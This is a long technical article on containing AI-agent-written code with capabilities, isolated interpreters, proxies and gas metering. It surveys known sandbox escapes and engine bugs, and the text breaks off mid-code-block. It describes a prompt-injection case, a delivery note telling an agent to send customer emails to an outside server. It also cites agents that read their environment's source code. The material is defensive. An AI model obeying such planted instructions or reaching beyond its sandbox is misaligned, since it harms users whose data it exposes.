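# Sandboxing Agent-Written Code with Capabilities and Gas Metering

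## Why applications run code written by an agent, and what they risk

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses and carries out actions towards a goal. Many agents work inside another application, such as a spreadsheet, a mail client or a shop's administration page, and act on that application's data. They usually act through tool calls, in which the model picks one operation from a list, the application performs it, and the model reads the result before picking the next. Alternatively, the model can write a short program for the application to run. This agent-written code is generated at run time and executed without human review. The host application, or host, is the application that starts the code, owns the data and controls what the code can access. As a precaution, the host can run the code in a sandbox, an execution environment from which code can affect the outside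 only in ways the host has allowed.

### One program instead of many calls

A running example, with invented numbers, makes the difference concrete. A shop's order page holds 2,000 orders. An employee asks the agent to flag every open order above €500 that has waited more than seven days. With tool calls, the agent first requests the orders, and the whole list enters the model's context, the text the model reads before each step. At a rough 20 tokens per order (a token is a word or a piece of one) that is 40,000 tokens. The model then has to find the matching orders by reading, and issue a separate call to flag each one. With code, the model needs to know only the names of the fields:

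```
for (const o of orders) {
  if (o.status === "open" && o.total > 500 && o.daysOpen > 7) {
    flag(o.id, "open for more than seven days");
  }
}
```

The host runs the loop, the order data stays out of the context, and ordinary arithmetic decides which totals exceed €500.

Cloudflare, which hosts other companies' websites and programs, named this approach "Code Mode" in September 2025. In *Code Mode*, Varda and Pai describe how the older method uses tokens. The model emits a special marker, then a structured message naming the tool and its arguments. The surrounding software pauses the model, performs the call and returns the result as text. When one call's output is the next call's input, the model has to copy the data itself. Their replacement converts the tools of an MCP server into a typed programming interface and gives the model a single tool that runs code. (MCP, the Model Context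 Protocol, is an open standard for connecting agents to outside services.) They guess that models do better this way because their training data contains a lot of real code but only contrived examples of tool calls.

Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, from November 2025, describes a second source of token use, the descriptions of all available tools, which many agents load before they read the request. In its example, an agent copies the transcript of a two-hour sales meeting from a document store into a customer database. The transcript passes through the model twice, which can add 50,000 tokens. Loading only the needed descriptions and moving the data in code reduces the total from 150,000 tokens to 2,000. The example illustrates the mechanism, but an average task is unlikely to see the same reduction.

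Cloudflare's headline figure is a saving of 81%, which Varda, Pai and Gupta give in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* without saying what they compared. The same number appears in *Cloudflare* (2025), a recap by the software company WorkOS of a stage demonstration by Rita Kozlov, a Cloudflare vice-president. Kozlov gave the same requests to two agents, one that made separate tool calls and one that wrote a program. For a request that produced 31 calendar events, both agents created them all, but the second used a loop and needed 81% fewer tokens. For a single event, the saving was 32%. The larger saving therefore came from a repetitive task that the vendor chose, though the order page has a task of that kind.

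Independent tests support this. In *Beyond Plain MCP*, Rai (2026) fixed the analysis plan in advance and ran three freely downloadable models on 119 task instances in a simulated company with 42 tools. Writing code instead of making plain tool calls cut the models' token use by 84%, 70% and 90%. The share of tasks solved rose from 86% to 99% for Qwen3.8-27B and from 36% to 56% for Nemotron-3-Nano, while Gemma-4-26B-A4B gained too little to rule out chance. When Rai removed the notes telling the models what each tool returns, the share fell to 66% for Gemma and 16% for Nemotron, both well below their results with plain tool calls. For the loop above to work, the host therefore has to tell the model that the field is `daysOpen` and that it holds a number.

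*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared code with tool calls across 14 commercial models on 309 benchmark tasks. Code was at least as accurate as tool calls for 11 models. The exceptions were GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini, which wrote line breaks as literal characters, so any script longer than one line failed with a syntax error. The advantage of code grew with the number of dependent steps and reached 18.8 percentage points for chains of 12 calls or more. That last result is weaker than it looks, because the test functions only recorded their arguments and returned no real data, so the models had to work out the intermediate values themselves.

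Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026), in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, also found that code used fewer tokens and turns than step-by-step calls, at mostly similar quality. Step-by-step calls still did better where each step depends on interpreting the result of the last, as in open-ended work with text. They found that running generated code greatly enlarges the attack surface, the set of places where an attacker can try to interfere.

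### Three sources of harm

In a 2026 conference talk, Agrawal (2026), in *Sandboxing AI-generated code*, sorts the dangers by how the harmful code comes about.

A model can write faulty code without an attacker's involvement. It can import a package that does not exist, write a recursion with no base case, or get a stopping condition wrong and produce an infinite loop. On the order page, the fault could be a `while` loop that never advances to the next order, or a reversed comparison that flags the wrong customers without causing a crash.

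Other code does its job but accesses more than the job requires. In Agrawal's example, a program generated to configure a database connection searches the server's environment variables for useful settings and in doing so reads every password and access key stored there. No one intended to steal these secrets, but a program that no one has reviewed has now read them, and they can end up in a log or in the model's context. Agents also overreach in practice. *Is this machine playing?* (2026), a study that places agents in simulated worlds, reports that in early runs without a sandbox, agents read the source code of their world or came across parallel runs and began interacting with them. No attacker was involved, though the paper mentions this only in an appendix and doesn't count how often it happened.

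Prompt injection is text in the data a model reads that makes it follow an attacker's instructions. In the indirect form, as Felendler and colleagues define it, the attacker plants the instructions in a document, a web page or the output of a tool, without talking to the model directly. For example, a customer of the shop could write in a delivery note that the agent should send all email addresses to a certain server. Having the model write code only partly protects against this. The model may write its first program before seeing any of the data, but it then reads the program's output and often writes another.

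### What eval hands over

The simplest way to run generated JavaScript is `eval`, a built-in function that takes a string and executes it as part of the program that called it. The generated code shares that program's memory, thread and global objects. In a browser, these objects include `document`, which lets code read and change the page, and `fetch`, which sends requests over the network. If the program calls `eval` directly inside one of its functions, the generated code can also read that function's local variables.

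On the order page, each source of harm can then affect the whole application. An endless loop freezes the page because it occupies the thread that also responds to clicks. A program that searches the page's variables for "everything about the order" finds the customers' emails and the session token, the string that proves to the server that the employee has logged in. A program influenced by the delivery note can call the refund function, or collect the emails and send them away with `fetch`. Agrawal makes the same point about servers, where programs inherit access to files, environment variables, databases and keys. A better model will write fewer faulty loops, but it won't change how much damage one bad program can do, because that depends on what the program can reach.

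This inherited power, which code has merely because of where it runs, is usually called ambient authority. A program for flagging late orders has network access because the page it runs in has `fetch`, though nobody decided to grant the program that access.

For code that nobody has read, it is much safer for a host to grant only the access the code needs than to list everything it must not touch. Agrawal compares the list to handing a visitor a master key and the names of ten thousand forbidden rooms, instead of keys to the three rooms they need. If the list omits a room, the visitor can walk in, but a visitor who is missing a key finds the door locked and complains.

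### Capabilities, and the four ways to obtain one

A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and permits its use. A plain name only identifies the resource. Under `eval`, code can reach the refund function just by using the name `refund`, because the language looks the name up in the surrounding program. In a capability system, code that contains the name still can't call the function unless it has been given a capability for it.

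Dennis and Van Horn, at the Massachusetts Institute of Technology, published the idea in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966), when many users' programs had begun to run side by side on one shared machine. In their design, every computation runs inside a "sphere of protection", which is defined by a list of capabilities. Each capability locates one object, such as a segment of memory, and states the permitted actions, such as reading without writing. A program uses a capability by giving its position in the list. According to *Early Capability Architectures*, a running process could also create an inferior sphere and copy a capability into it with specified access rights. A host does nearly the same thing when it starts agent-written code. Dennis and Van Horn also gave each user or group an allotment of computing resources and had the supervisor, the system's trusted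 core, step in when someone exceeded it.

Forty years later, Miller's doctoral thesis at Johns Hopkins University, *Robust Composition* (2006), developed the idea for programming languages as the object-capability model. The model treats a running program as a graph of objects, in which one object can affect another only by sending a message along a reference it holds. A reference identifies an object and inseparably carries both the permission and the means to access it. The model holds only if the language prevents code from forging a reference out of a number, reaching into another object's private state, or sharing changeable global variables, as code on ordinary web pages does all the time.

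Under these rules, an object, Bob, can get a reference to another object, Carol, in four ways. In two of them, a third object, Alice, gives Bob the reference.

| Way | Rule | On the order page |
|---|---|---|
| Initial conditions | Bob already refers to Carol at the first moment under analysis | Built-in objects, such as the array functions, exist before the agent's code starts |
| Parenthood | Bob creates Carol, and at that moment only Bob refers to her | The code builds its own list of late orders |
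| Endowment | Alice creates Bob and equips him with a reference to Carol that she already holds | The host starts the code with references to the orders and to `flag` |
| Introduction | Alice refers to both, and sends Bob a message that contains a reference to Carol | The host answers a call from the code with a further object |

Miller sums the rules up as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If no chain of these steps leads from the agent's code to the refund function, the code cannot call it, regardless of who influenced the model or how clever the program is. The host's developers, who cannot read every program that a model will write, can therefore review a short list of references instead. They should look hardest at the first and last rows of the table, where unintended access tends to go unnoticed, such as through a global function that someone forgot to remove or a returned order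 that carries a link to the customer's full record.

The capability rules do not cover plain data, such as numbers and text, which Miller treats separately because anyone who knows or guesses a piece of data has it. The session token is a string of characters, so controlling references cannot take it back once it has leaked, and the host has to keep it out of the sandbox altogether. The rules also control only what code can reach, not what it does there. Code that holds `flag` can flag all 2,000 orders. Felendler and colleagues likewise conclude that isolation does not stop attacks that stay within the operations the sandbox permits.

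### The order page and the design

The exposed state is the part of the data and operations that the host makes reachable. For the order page, it consists of each order's id, total, status and days open, and one operation, `flag(id, reason)`. The loop shown earlier needs nothing else. The host does not expose the customers' emails, the session token, the refund function or the page itself.

The design for containing the code has three parts. First, the host removes ambient authority by running the code in an isolated interpreter with no access to the page document, the network or the host's variables. Second, the host injects proxies into the interpreter, which are stand-in objects that pass permitted operations on to the real objects in the host. Third, the host meters the work by giving the program a fixed budget of abstract computing units, called gas. Running code uses up gas, and the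 interpreter stops the program when the budget runs out. Metering has to be a separate part because an endless loop needs no capabilities, so restricting them can't stop it.

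## Running the code with no document, no network and no host globals

The loop for the order page needs a list, a few comparisons and the function `flag`. It doesn't need `document` or `fetch`, which aren't part of the JavaScript language. The language standard covers only objects for computing, such as `Array`, `Math`, `JSON` and `Promise`. An engine, the program that reads and runs JavaScript, creates these built-in objects each time it sets up a new environment. The browser then adds its own objects and functions, including `document` and `fetch`, to the environment's global object, where the engine looks up any name it can't find in the surrounding code. The page's scripts add more names, such as `refund`.

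A host can remove this ambient authority by restricting what agent-written code can access in the engine that runs the page, or by starting a second engine with nothing added to it. Using the existing engine gives faster code and easier debugging, but researchers have repeatedly broken sandboxes of this kind.

### Restricting code inside the host's own engine

The crudest method is to wrap the code in a function whose parameters have the names `document` and `fetch`, and to pass nothing for them:

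```
const run = new Function("document", "fetch", "orders", "flag", agentCode);
run(undefined, undefined, orders, flag);
```

When the agent-written code uses `fetch`, the name resolves to the empty parameter. The real function still exists, though, and the code can reach it by any route that avoids the name. The obvious route is the global object, which is also available as `globalThis`. Even if the host hides that name too, the built-in objects remain. Every array, function and error links to the built-ins of the environment that created it, including the function constructor, which turns text into new code that runs with that environment's globals. An object that comes from the page can therefore lead back to the page's `fetch`. In terms of Miller's rules, the code had a path to the network from the start, by initial conditions, and hiding the name did not remove it.

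Shared built-ins can also expose the page's data to the sandboxed code. If that code replaces the `filter` function that all arrays share, the page will call the replacement the next time it filters a list and pass it the list's contents.

Google's Caja, from 2008, dealt with these routes by rewriting the code before running it. Miller designed the JavaScript part. The translator turned each program into a single function that could use only names it defined or received from the page. A program that used `document` got whatever the page had supplied, typically a wrapper that filtered HTML. Caja also froze shared functions and prototypes, the objects from which other objects inherit their methods. It rejected any name ending in two underscores, because in Firefox one such name led from an object to its prototype.

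A rule like the last one covers only a route that somebody has already noticed. Bug hunter Michał Bentkowski found flaws in Caja that could have let attackers run scripts on Google Docs pages, according to SecurityWeek's *Google Patches Vulnerabilities in Caja Tool*. Google fixed those flaws, but later stopped actively developing Caja and archived the project on 31 January 2021. Google explained in its notice that Caja had not kept up with web security research, and that its own engineers and outside researchers had reported several vulnerabilities. Google recommended the Closure toolkit to people who used Caja to clean HTML and CSS, but Closure does not replace Caja for running untrusted JavaScript.

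Hardened JavaScript, a proposed addition to the language, continues Caja's work, and the *SES* library implements it in today's engines. The host first calls `lockdown()`, which freezes the built-in objects that all code can reach, so no program can replace `filter` for the others. It then creates a compartment, an environment with its own global object. The compartment shares frozen built-ins such as `Array` with the page, but its global object has no `fetch` or `document` unless the host adds them. The library also blocks the route through the function constructor. Each compartment gets its own constructor, whose code sees only that compartment's globals, and any shared function's constructor link now leads to a dummy that only throws errors.

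The cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask runs other developers' add-ons this way. According to MetaMask's *Snaps execution environment*, an add-on gets the `fetch` global only if it has a network permission.

A compartment is much stronger than a hidden name because it blocks whole kinds of routes to the host's globals. But the page's real `fetch` is still in the same engine, and the host can accidentally give the code a way to reach it. Suppose the order page passes the code a table row to highlight. Every element links to the document that contains it, so the code can now reach the whole page. Freezing the row wouldn't help, since a frozen object's links and functions still work.

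### How vm2 and Figma's first sandbox failed

On servers, many JavaScript programs run in Node, which uses V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. Node has no `document`, but it gives programs access to files, the network and other programs. Its `vm` module runs code with a separate global object inside the same process, but it is not a security boundary. The *vm2* library tries to provide one, and its documentation includes a single line of code that shuts down the host from inside `vm`. vm2 blocks that line by placing proxies between the sandbox and the host, which must intercept every interaction and recognise host objects in whatever form they cross, including inside an error or as the result of a delayed operation. The library's maintainers warn that researchers keep finding ways out and will probably find more.

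Patrik Simek, the founder of vm2, gave up on the project in 2023 when faced with an escape "so complicated that fixing it seems impossible". He recommended isolated-vm, a library that gives the code a V8 instance with its own memory. He revived vm2 in October 2025, as heise online's *JavaScript Sandbox vm2* recounts, but by January 2026 it needed a fix for a new critical escape, and a working demonstration was already public. In May, GitLab's *CVE-2026-26956* (2026) recorded another escape, which worked on Node 25 without host cooperation.

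These were two of many. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Vm2 package* lists more than 40 entries for 2026. Many apply only if the host has let the sandbox load a particular Node module, and some concern crashes or time limits rather than escapes. The high count also partly reflects how hard people are looking. But the same kinds of flaw recur. Lists of forbidden modules omitted one, or blocked it under only one of its names. Fixes for earlier escapes closed one route but left a similar one open. In several cases, sandboxed code could still modify built-ins that the host was using. New features in Node and V8 opened further routes, which is hard to avoid when a sandbox has to account for every feature of the engine it shares with the host.

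Figma, whose design tool runs plugins by outside developers in the browser, abandoned the shared engine after one incident. Figma's *How to build a plugin system on the web* describes the designs it considered before its first launch, including a separate engine. It chose the Realms shim, a library from Agoric, which now relies on Hardened JavaScript. On 14 September 2019 someone published a vulnerability in the shim, and a private report of several more followed two days later. Figma's *An update on plugin security* (2019) traces them to a common cause. One engine handled the objects on both sides of the sandbox boundary, and the shim could mistake an object from outside for one from inside, or the reverse.

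Figma patched the flaws and found no evidence that any plugin had exploited them, but it still replaced the shim. The new sandbox went live on 25 September, nine days after work on it began. Figma could switch this quickly because it had kept the design as a fallback and had built its software to make sandboxes interchangeable. Some plugins became slower, which Figma accepted in exchange for better security. Figma's staff review new plugins before publication, a step that agent-written code doesn't go through, but they check only the quality of the user experience because a reviewer can easily miss malicious code.

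### Giving the code an engine of its own

Figma switched to QuickJS, a small JavaScript engine written in C, and compiled it to WebAssembly. WebAssembly, or Wasm, is a portable bytecode whose programs can call only the outside functions given to them as imports. A Wasm program keeps its data in a linear memory, one long block of bytes, and can't read or write outside that block.

On the order page, the browser first loads the QuickJS module and reserves a linear memory for it. The page then calls a function in the module that sets up a JavaScript environment, and QuickJS builds its own `Array`, `Math` and `JSON` inside that memory. Next, the page adds `orders` and `flag` as proxies. Finally it copies the text of the agent's program into the memory and has QuickJS run it. Inside, the program would find the following:

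```
typeof Array      // "function": QuickJS created it
typeof orders     // "object": the host injected it
typeof fetch      // "undefined"
typeof document   // "undefined"
```

Calling `fetch` has the same result as calling a misspelled function name, because QuickJS looks up globals only in its own global object, which has no such function. Its built-ins don't give access to the page either, because they link only to other objects in the same linear memory. Figma points out that the mix-up that broke the Realms shim can't recur, because the two engines represent objects too differently. To the page, a QuickJS array is just bytes. A careless host can still undo some of this isolation. QuickJS comes with optional modules for files and operating-system functions, so the host has to leave them out or give the Wasm module no imports through which they could work.

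LangChain, which makes software for building agents, chose the same combination for agent-written scripts. *Running Untrusted Agent Code Without a Sandbox* (Lovell, 2026) contrasts it with a container, which packages a program with its own files and system libraries. A container starts out like a whole computer, with a file system and a command line, and its operator takes abilities away, whereas an interpreter starts with variables, functions and loops, and its operator adds abilities one at a time. Because the whole interpreter is in one block of memory, LangChain's software can save that block when a script needs a person's approval, then resume the script where it stopped hours or days later.

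#### V8 isolates and the network setting

Cloudflare's Dynamic Workers each run code in their own isolate, an instance of the V8 engine with separate memory and built-ins. A Worker is a program on Cloudflare's servers, and a Dynamic Worker is one that another Worker starts with code supplied at run time. A bare isolate has no more network access than QuickJS does, but Cloudflare adds functions that server programs commonly use, including `fetch` and `connect`, which opens a direct network connection. There is no `document` because the code doesn't run in a web page.

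A setting called `globalOutbound` then determines what `fetch` can do. If the host sets it to `null`, every call to `fetch` or `connect` throws an error, and the code can use only its bindings, which is Cloudflare's name for the capabilities the host passes in. Cloudflare's *Egress control* calls this the most secure way to design such a sandbox. If the host leaves the setting out, the Dynamic Worker normally inherits the network access of the Worker that started it, which usually means the public internet.

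The two outcomes differ by one line in the host's code. That line is easy to forget, and ordinary testing won't reveal the mistake because the late-orders program never calls `fetch` and runs the same either way. A host that relies on this setting should have an automated test that calls `fetch` from inside the sandbox and checks that the call fails with an error.

The setting also accepts a gateway, which is host code that receives every outgoing request and can block it, log it or attach a password that the sandboxed code never sees. This is useful for existing libraries that have to make web requests. Varda and colleagues still prefer to give the sandboxed code a few purpose-built functions, because a gateway has to interpret every request in full, including its headers and parameters, to decide whether to allow it.

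#### A Wasm module with chosen imports

The code can also run without a JavaScript engine. Martin Monperrus, a software researcher at KTH in Stockholm, built a coding agent that can run only Wasm modules it has compiled itself. The agent writes a program in Rust, compiles it into a module and executes it with Wasmtime, an engine that runs Wasm outside the browser. A module has to list each outside function it needs, and Wasmtime won't start the module if one of them is missing. Monperrus's modules get text input and output and, on request, particular directories, but no network connections.

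The agent requests a directory in an argument of its tool call, so the request appears in the log. Anyone who reads the log can see which directories a program could have changed, without understanding the program. This design is awkward for the order page, though, because the host would need a Rust compiler and each small script would have to wait to be compiled. In Monperrus's demonstration, a program that prints ten prime numbers compiled to a 1.75 MB module.

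### When the engine has bugs

A separate engine gives the code no functions for reaching the outside world, but it is a large program with bugs. Code that can corrupt the engine's memory may be able to get out even without a `fetch` function. The options differ in their trusted computing base (the components that must work correctly for the containment to hold) and in what a memory bug in the JavaScript engine would expose.

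| Option | Trusted computing base | What a memory bug in the JavaScript engine could expose |
|---|---|---|
| Hardened JavaScript | The page's engine, the freezing and compartment code, every object the host passes in | The page's memory |
| vm2 | V8, Node, the proxies around every interaction | The server process |
| V8 isolate | V8 and the software that adds functions to it | The process that holds the isolate, unless another layer stops the attack |
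| QuickJS in Wasm | The Wasm engine and the imported functions | QuickJS's own linear memory |
| Wasm module in Wasmtime | Wasmtime's compiler and runtime, the imported functions | Not applicable, though a bug in Wasmtime itself could expose the host |

V8 has the worst recent record of the engines here, partly because so many people attack it. In 2026, through early September, Google fixed seven Chrome flaws that attackers were already exploiting, and four were in V8, according to *Google fixes the seventh actively exploited Chrome zero-day of 2026* (Paganini, 2026). *Chrome Update Patches Exploited XML Zero-Day, Eighth This Year* (Kovacs, 2026) reports an eighth in November, in the component that handles XML, a text format for data. Cloudflare, which sells a sandbox built on V8, acknowledges the problem. Varda and colleagues write that security bugs are more common in V8 than in typical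 hypervisors, the programs that divide one physical computer into several virtual machines.

QuickJS has memory bugs too. In January 2026 the Spanish cybersecurity institute INCIBE published entries on two in QuickJS-ng, a separately maintained version of the engine. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-0821* (2026) describes the engine writing past the end of a reserved block of memory, and *CVE-2026-1144* (2026) describes it using memory it has already released. Exploits for both were public.

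How much such a flaw matters depends on where QuickJS runs. If a host builds QuickJS directly into its own program, a stray write can damage the host's memory. Inside Wasm, the write stays in the linear memory, because the engine "sits behind the boundary rather than beside it", as Lovell puts it. The attacker then controls the interpreter but can reach the host only through the imports. The attacker can still call those imports with any arguments and skip any checks that run inside the sandbox, so the host has to check the arguments itself.

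In that case the Wasm engine has to contain the code, and Wasm engines also had serious security flaws in 2026. On 9 April 2026 the Bytecode Alliance, the group of companies and universities behind Wasmtime, published 12 security advisories, three times as many as in all of 2025. Two described critical flaws that could let code escape the sandbox, doubling the number of critical advisories in the project's history. Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) explains that the team found 11 of the 12 itself by having language models search the source code for three weeks. The search found nothing new after the second week, which is mildly reassuring. Another release followed six weeks later, and Crichton's *Upcoming Security Release for Wasmtime on 2026-05-21* (2026) announced in advance that it would fix a high-severity flaw.

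Neither of the critical flaws affected Wasmtime's main compiler on x86-64 processors, the combination that most production systems have used and that gets the most scrutiny. One flaw was in a newer compiler, and the other was in the main compiler's output for ARM processors. Researchers had mathematically verified the part of the compiler that contained the ARM error, but the code later changed and nobody updated the mathematical model, so the proof held only for the older version. When the team updated the model, verification found the bug.

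Errors of this sort, in which a compiler turns harmless-looking Wasm into faulty machine code, are easiest to exploit for someone who can choose the Wasm instructions. Under Monperrus's design, an attacker who controls the agent can do that. With QuickJS, the Wasm engine always compiles the same module, and the agent's program is only data for that module, so an attacker would need the fault to occur in the QuickJS module itself. The same reasoning applies in a browser, where V8 runs both the page and the QuickJS module. V8 remains part of the trusted computing base, but the agent's JavaScript never reaches V8's JavaScript compiler.

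### Leaks through timing

Code can sometimes learn secrets even when the engine has no bugs, by exploiting how processors save time. A processor starts on instructions before it knows whether the program will need them, and throws away the results if it guessed wrong. The discarded work still changes which data sits in the cache, the processor's small, fast memory. A program can detect those changes by measuring how long reads take, and use them to work out the contents of memory it has no permission to read. Researchers published the best-known attacks of this type, called Spectre, in 2018.

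Such an attack requires a secret in the same process and a precise way to measure time. The first condition is common. Dynamic Workers usually run on the same thread as the Worker that started them, and in the order page's tab, the QuickJS memory and the session token share a process.

A host has more control over the clock. *SES* withholds the current time and the random-number function from compartments unless the host adds them, though mainly to stop programs from using them to signal to each other. The loop on the order page needs neither, since it receives `daysOpen` as a finished number. Without a clock, code has more trouble measuring time, but it might still compare how long two operations take by other means, such as the timing of replies from the host. Wasmtime includes some protection against Spectre, and Cloudflare hired researchers to develop defences of its own, but it is simpler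 to keep the secret out of the process.

### Adding layers

The usual protection against engine bugs is a second barrier behind the engine, so that an attacker needs two unrelated flaws. Chrome, for example, runs web pages in separate operating-system processes with few rights. According to Paganini, September's V8 flaw let an attacker run any code, but only inside Chrome's process sandbox.

On the order page, Chrome's barrier protects the employee's computer and the other websites they have open, but not the customers' emails or the session token, which are in the same process as the interpreter. To protect those too, the host can load the interpreter in a frame from a different website address. Chrome on desktop computers normally runs such a frame in its own process. The page and the interpreter can then communicate only by sending messages, so the proxies become slower and every call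 has to wait for a reply.

Cloudflare can't give every isolate its own process without losing much of the speed that isolates are meant to provide. According to Varda and colleagues, it puts a second sandbox around the isolates and separates customers whose code looks risky from the rest. It also uses memory protection keys, a processor feature that blocks access to marked regions of memory even from within the same process. Its systems install V8 security fixes within hours, sooner than Chrome gets them. They also scan code for malicious patterns, but this is the weakest measure because a scan can detect only patterns its developers anticipated.

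Patching quickly is especially important after the Wasmtime search. Attackers can also use language models to look for flaws, and they can learn where to look from a published fix. Browser updates don't fix a product's own bundled copy of QuickJS or Wasmtime, so the product's developers have to notice each advisory and ship a new version themselves.

Virtual machines offer a stronger barrier because the processor helps to separate their memory. They used to start far too slowly for a ten-line script. Micro-VMs reduce the delay by leaving out most of what a full virtual machine contains. Firecracker, which Amazon developed, boots a minimal operating system. Hyperlight, an open-source library that began at Microsoft, does without one and creates a very small virtual machine for a single function call. A host on a server can run a Wasm engine inside such a machine, so that hostile code would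 have to break out of both. A host running in a browser tab can't do this.

### Start-up time and memory

Start-up time and memory use matter for agent-written code because each program is typically short and runs once. Varda and colleagues estimate that a container takes hundreds of milliseconds to start and uses hundreds of megabytes of memory, while an isolate takes a few milliseconds and uses a few megabytes. Cloudflare sells both, but it is using these figures to promote isolates. At 200 MB per container and 3 MB per isolate, a thousand agents running code at once would need 200 GB with containers or 3 GB with isolates.

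Startup time affects security as well as the bill. An operator whose containers start slowly will be tempted to keep a few running and reuse them, and then one task can read files or variables that another left behind. If an environment starts in a few milliseconds, the operator can discard it after every program.

In a browser, the main drawback is the size of the download. In *MicroQuickJS*, Willison (2025) reported that a test page with QuickJS transferred 675 KB, while one with MicroQuickJS, a smaller engine by the same programmer, transferred 120 KB. MicroQuickJS can run a program in as little as 10 kB of memory and has no functions for files or the network. However, it supports only part of JavaScript, so a model that writes ordinary modern code will sometimes use an unsupported feature, and the host would have to list those features in its instructions to the model.

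QuickJS also runs code more slowly than V8, which compiles frequently used code to machine instructions. An employee wouldn't notice the difference with 2,000 orders and three comparisons each. It would matter for heavy calculations over large tables, where a host on a server has good reason to choose an isolate despite the extra work of securing V8.

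## Proxies: how the code reaches the state it has been given

A newly created interpreter has no access to the orders either. The host has to give the late-orders program the data and a way to flag an order, without also giving it everything those objects link to in the page. It does this with proxies, which are stand-in objects inside the sandbox.

### One call across the boundary

Suppose the program reaches order A-1042 and calls `flag("A-1042", "open for more than seven days")`. In the QuickJS sandbox, `flag` is a small function inside the interpreter. It calls one of the Wasm module's imports and passes a number that identifies the corresponding host function. The host looks the number up in a table, copies the two strings out of the linear memory and checks the copies. If they pass, it runs the real flagging function on the page's data and writes the result into the linear memory. The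 interpreter turns the result into a JavaScript value, and the program moves on to the next order.

The host has to copy each argument before checking it. An argument can be an object with a getter, a function that runs whenever something reads a property. A hostile getter can return a permitted order id when the host checks it and a different one when the host uses it. The host prevents this by reading the value once, then checking and using only the copy. The check also has to run on the host's side, where an attacker who has taken over the interpreter can't skip it.

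Dynamic Workers do the same thing by remote procedure call (RPC), which makes a message to another program look like an ordinary function call. Cloudflare calls the proxy a "stub". Cloudflare's *Cap'n Web* (2025) describes the messages. Each side keeps a numbered table of the objects it has exposed to the other, which starts with a single entry. A call consists of an entry number, a method name and the arguments. A number only selects from the table for that connection, so hostile code can't reach an object that the host never exposed by guessing numbers. Dennis and Van Horn's programs picked capabilities from their lists in much the same way.

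Hosts usually describe their functions, such as `flag(id: string, reason: string)`, to the model in TypeScript, which is JavaScript with type annotations. The annotations disappear before the program runs, so, as Cloudflare points out, the RPC system won't stop a malicious caller from sending arguments of the wrong type. The host needs its own run-time checks to refuse, for example, a list of 10,000 ids or a reason 50 million characters long. Libraries such as Zod generate these checks from a description of the expected data.

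### Copies, live views and write access

The host can hand over the orders as a copy, as a live view, or as something the code can change.

| What the code gets | Staleness | Round trips | Main risk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Copied snapshot | Grows from the moment of copying | One for the whole list | The host can't take a copied field back |
| Live read-only proxy | Each read is current, but the data can change between two reads | One for each read | A property or method returns a real object |
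| Writable proxy | As for the live proxy | One for each read or write | Faulty or hostile code changes real data |

The late-orders loop suits a snapshot because, after one transfer of 2,000 short records, every comparison happens inside the sandbox. With a live proxy, the program would make a host call for the status of each order, then for the total of each open order, and then for the age of each open order above €500. If 600 orders are open and 150 of those exceed €500, the reads alone take 2,750 host calls, and gas may not count the work those calls cause in the host.

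Live proxies can also break ordinary code. In Cloudflare's system, reading a property on a stub returns a promise, an object standing for a value that will arrive later. The test `o.status === "open"` would always be false, because it would compare a promise with text. The program would flag nothing and report no error. To prevent this, the host has to declare the property as a promise, so that the model writes `await o.status`.

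Cap'n Web can save round trips when one call depends on another. The program can use the promise from the first call as an argument to the second, and both travel in one message. A `map` function extends this to lists. It runs the program's callback once with a placeholder, records the calls the callback makes, and sends the recording to the other side, which repeats it for every element. Because the callback never receives a real value, it can't test whether a total exceeds €500. Filtering the orders still requires either copying the data or adding a filter function to the host.

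A snapshot may be out of date by the time the program acts on it. A colleague might ship A-1042 two seconds after the host takes the snapshot, and the program would then flag an order that is no longer open. The host can catch this by checking the order's current status inside the real `flag` function. This gives the order page most of the benefit of live data and requires only one host call per flag.

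For writes, a named operation like `flag` is usually safer than a property that the code can assign. If the program can set `order.status` to anything, the host has to work out from the new value whether the change was legitimate. A host can also hold changes back before applying them. *Transaction-based Sandboxing for JavaScript* (2016) describes a sandbox that redirects every write to a shadow object, so the original doesn't change. In Cloudflare's file library for agents, according to Varda and colleagues, the program prepares a set of edits and then passes them all to the host to apply. If one write fails, the library undoes the earlier ones. On the order page, a host that collected the flags first could show the employee the list before saving it.

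### Offering less than the real object

Suppose the page keeps its orders in an object called `store`, with methods for reading, flagging, refunding and deleting. Giving the agent's program `store` would let it do all four. The sketches below run in the host and assume a separate engine or Hardened JavaScript, because in an ordinary shared engine the program could reach the page's function constructor through any host function.

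The simplest remedy is a facade, an object that offers fewer methods than the one behind it:

```
const orderDesk = {
  flag: (id, reason) => store.flag(id, reason),
};
```

The arrow function uses `store`, but JavaScript has no operation for extracting a variable from inside a function. The program can call `orderDesk.flag` but cannot get from there to `store.refund`.

A facade is one form of attenuation, the practice of making a weaker capability from a stronger one. Attenuation can also restrict what a single method does. If the agent helps only one of the shop's warehouses, the host can make a `flag` function for that warehouse:

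```
const flagIn = (warehouse) => (id, reason) => {
  if (store.get(id)?.warehouse !== warehouse) {
    throw new Error("not an order of this warehouse");
  }
  store.flag(id, reason);
};
```

The host can restrict access with ordinary code instead of a separate permission system. In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro treat read-only access to a file as full access to a different object, whose methods can only query the file. The host can restrict that object further by wrapping it in another.

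Neither object expires. Miller stresses that a plain reference gives its holder unconditional and perpetual access, so a host that wants to withdraw access later has to prepare for it. The standard solution dates from 1974 and carries the name of its inventor, Redell. Redell's "caretaker" is a forwarder with a switch:

```
function makeRevocable(flag) {
  let enabled = true;
  return {
    flag(id, reason) {
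      if (!enabled) throw new Error("revoked");
      flag(id, reason);
    },
    revoke() { enabled = false; },
  };
}
```

The host gives the program only the new `flag` and keeps `revoke`. After the host calls `revoke`, the program still has its reference but can no longer use it to reach the real function. Yet some researchers argued for decades that capability systems could not support revocation. Miller traces the mistake to looking only at direct references. The program never had a direct reference to the real function, so by that view there was nothing to revoke.

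Throwing away the whole sandbox after each program has the same effect, so the switch matters mainly for access that might outlive its task. Once the program has read data such as an email address, the host can't take it back and can only stop the program from reading more.

### When `order.customer` returns the real customer

A developer who wants to give the program live orders might write a general read-only wrapper with JavaScript's built-in `Proxy`, which intercepts operations on an object:

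```
const readOnly = (target) => new Proxy(target, {
  set() { throw new TypeError("read-only"); },
});
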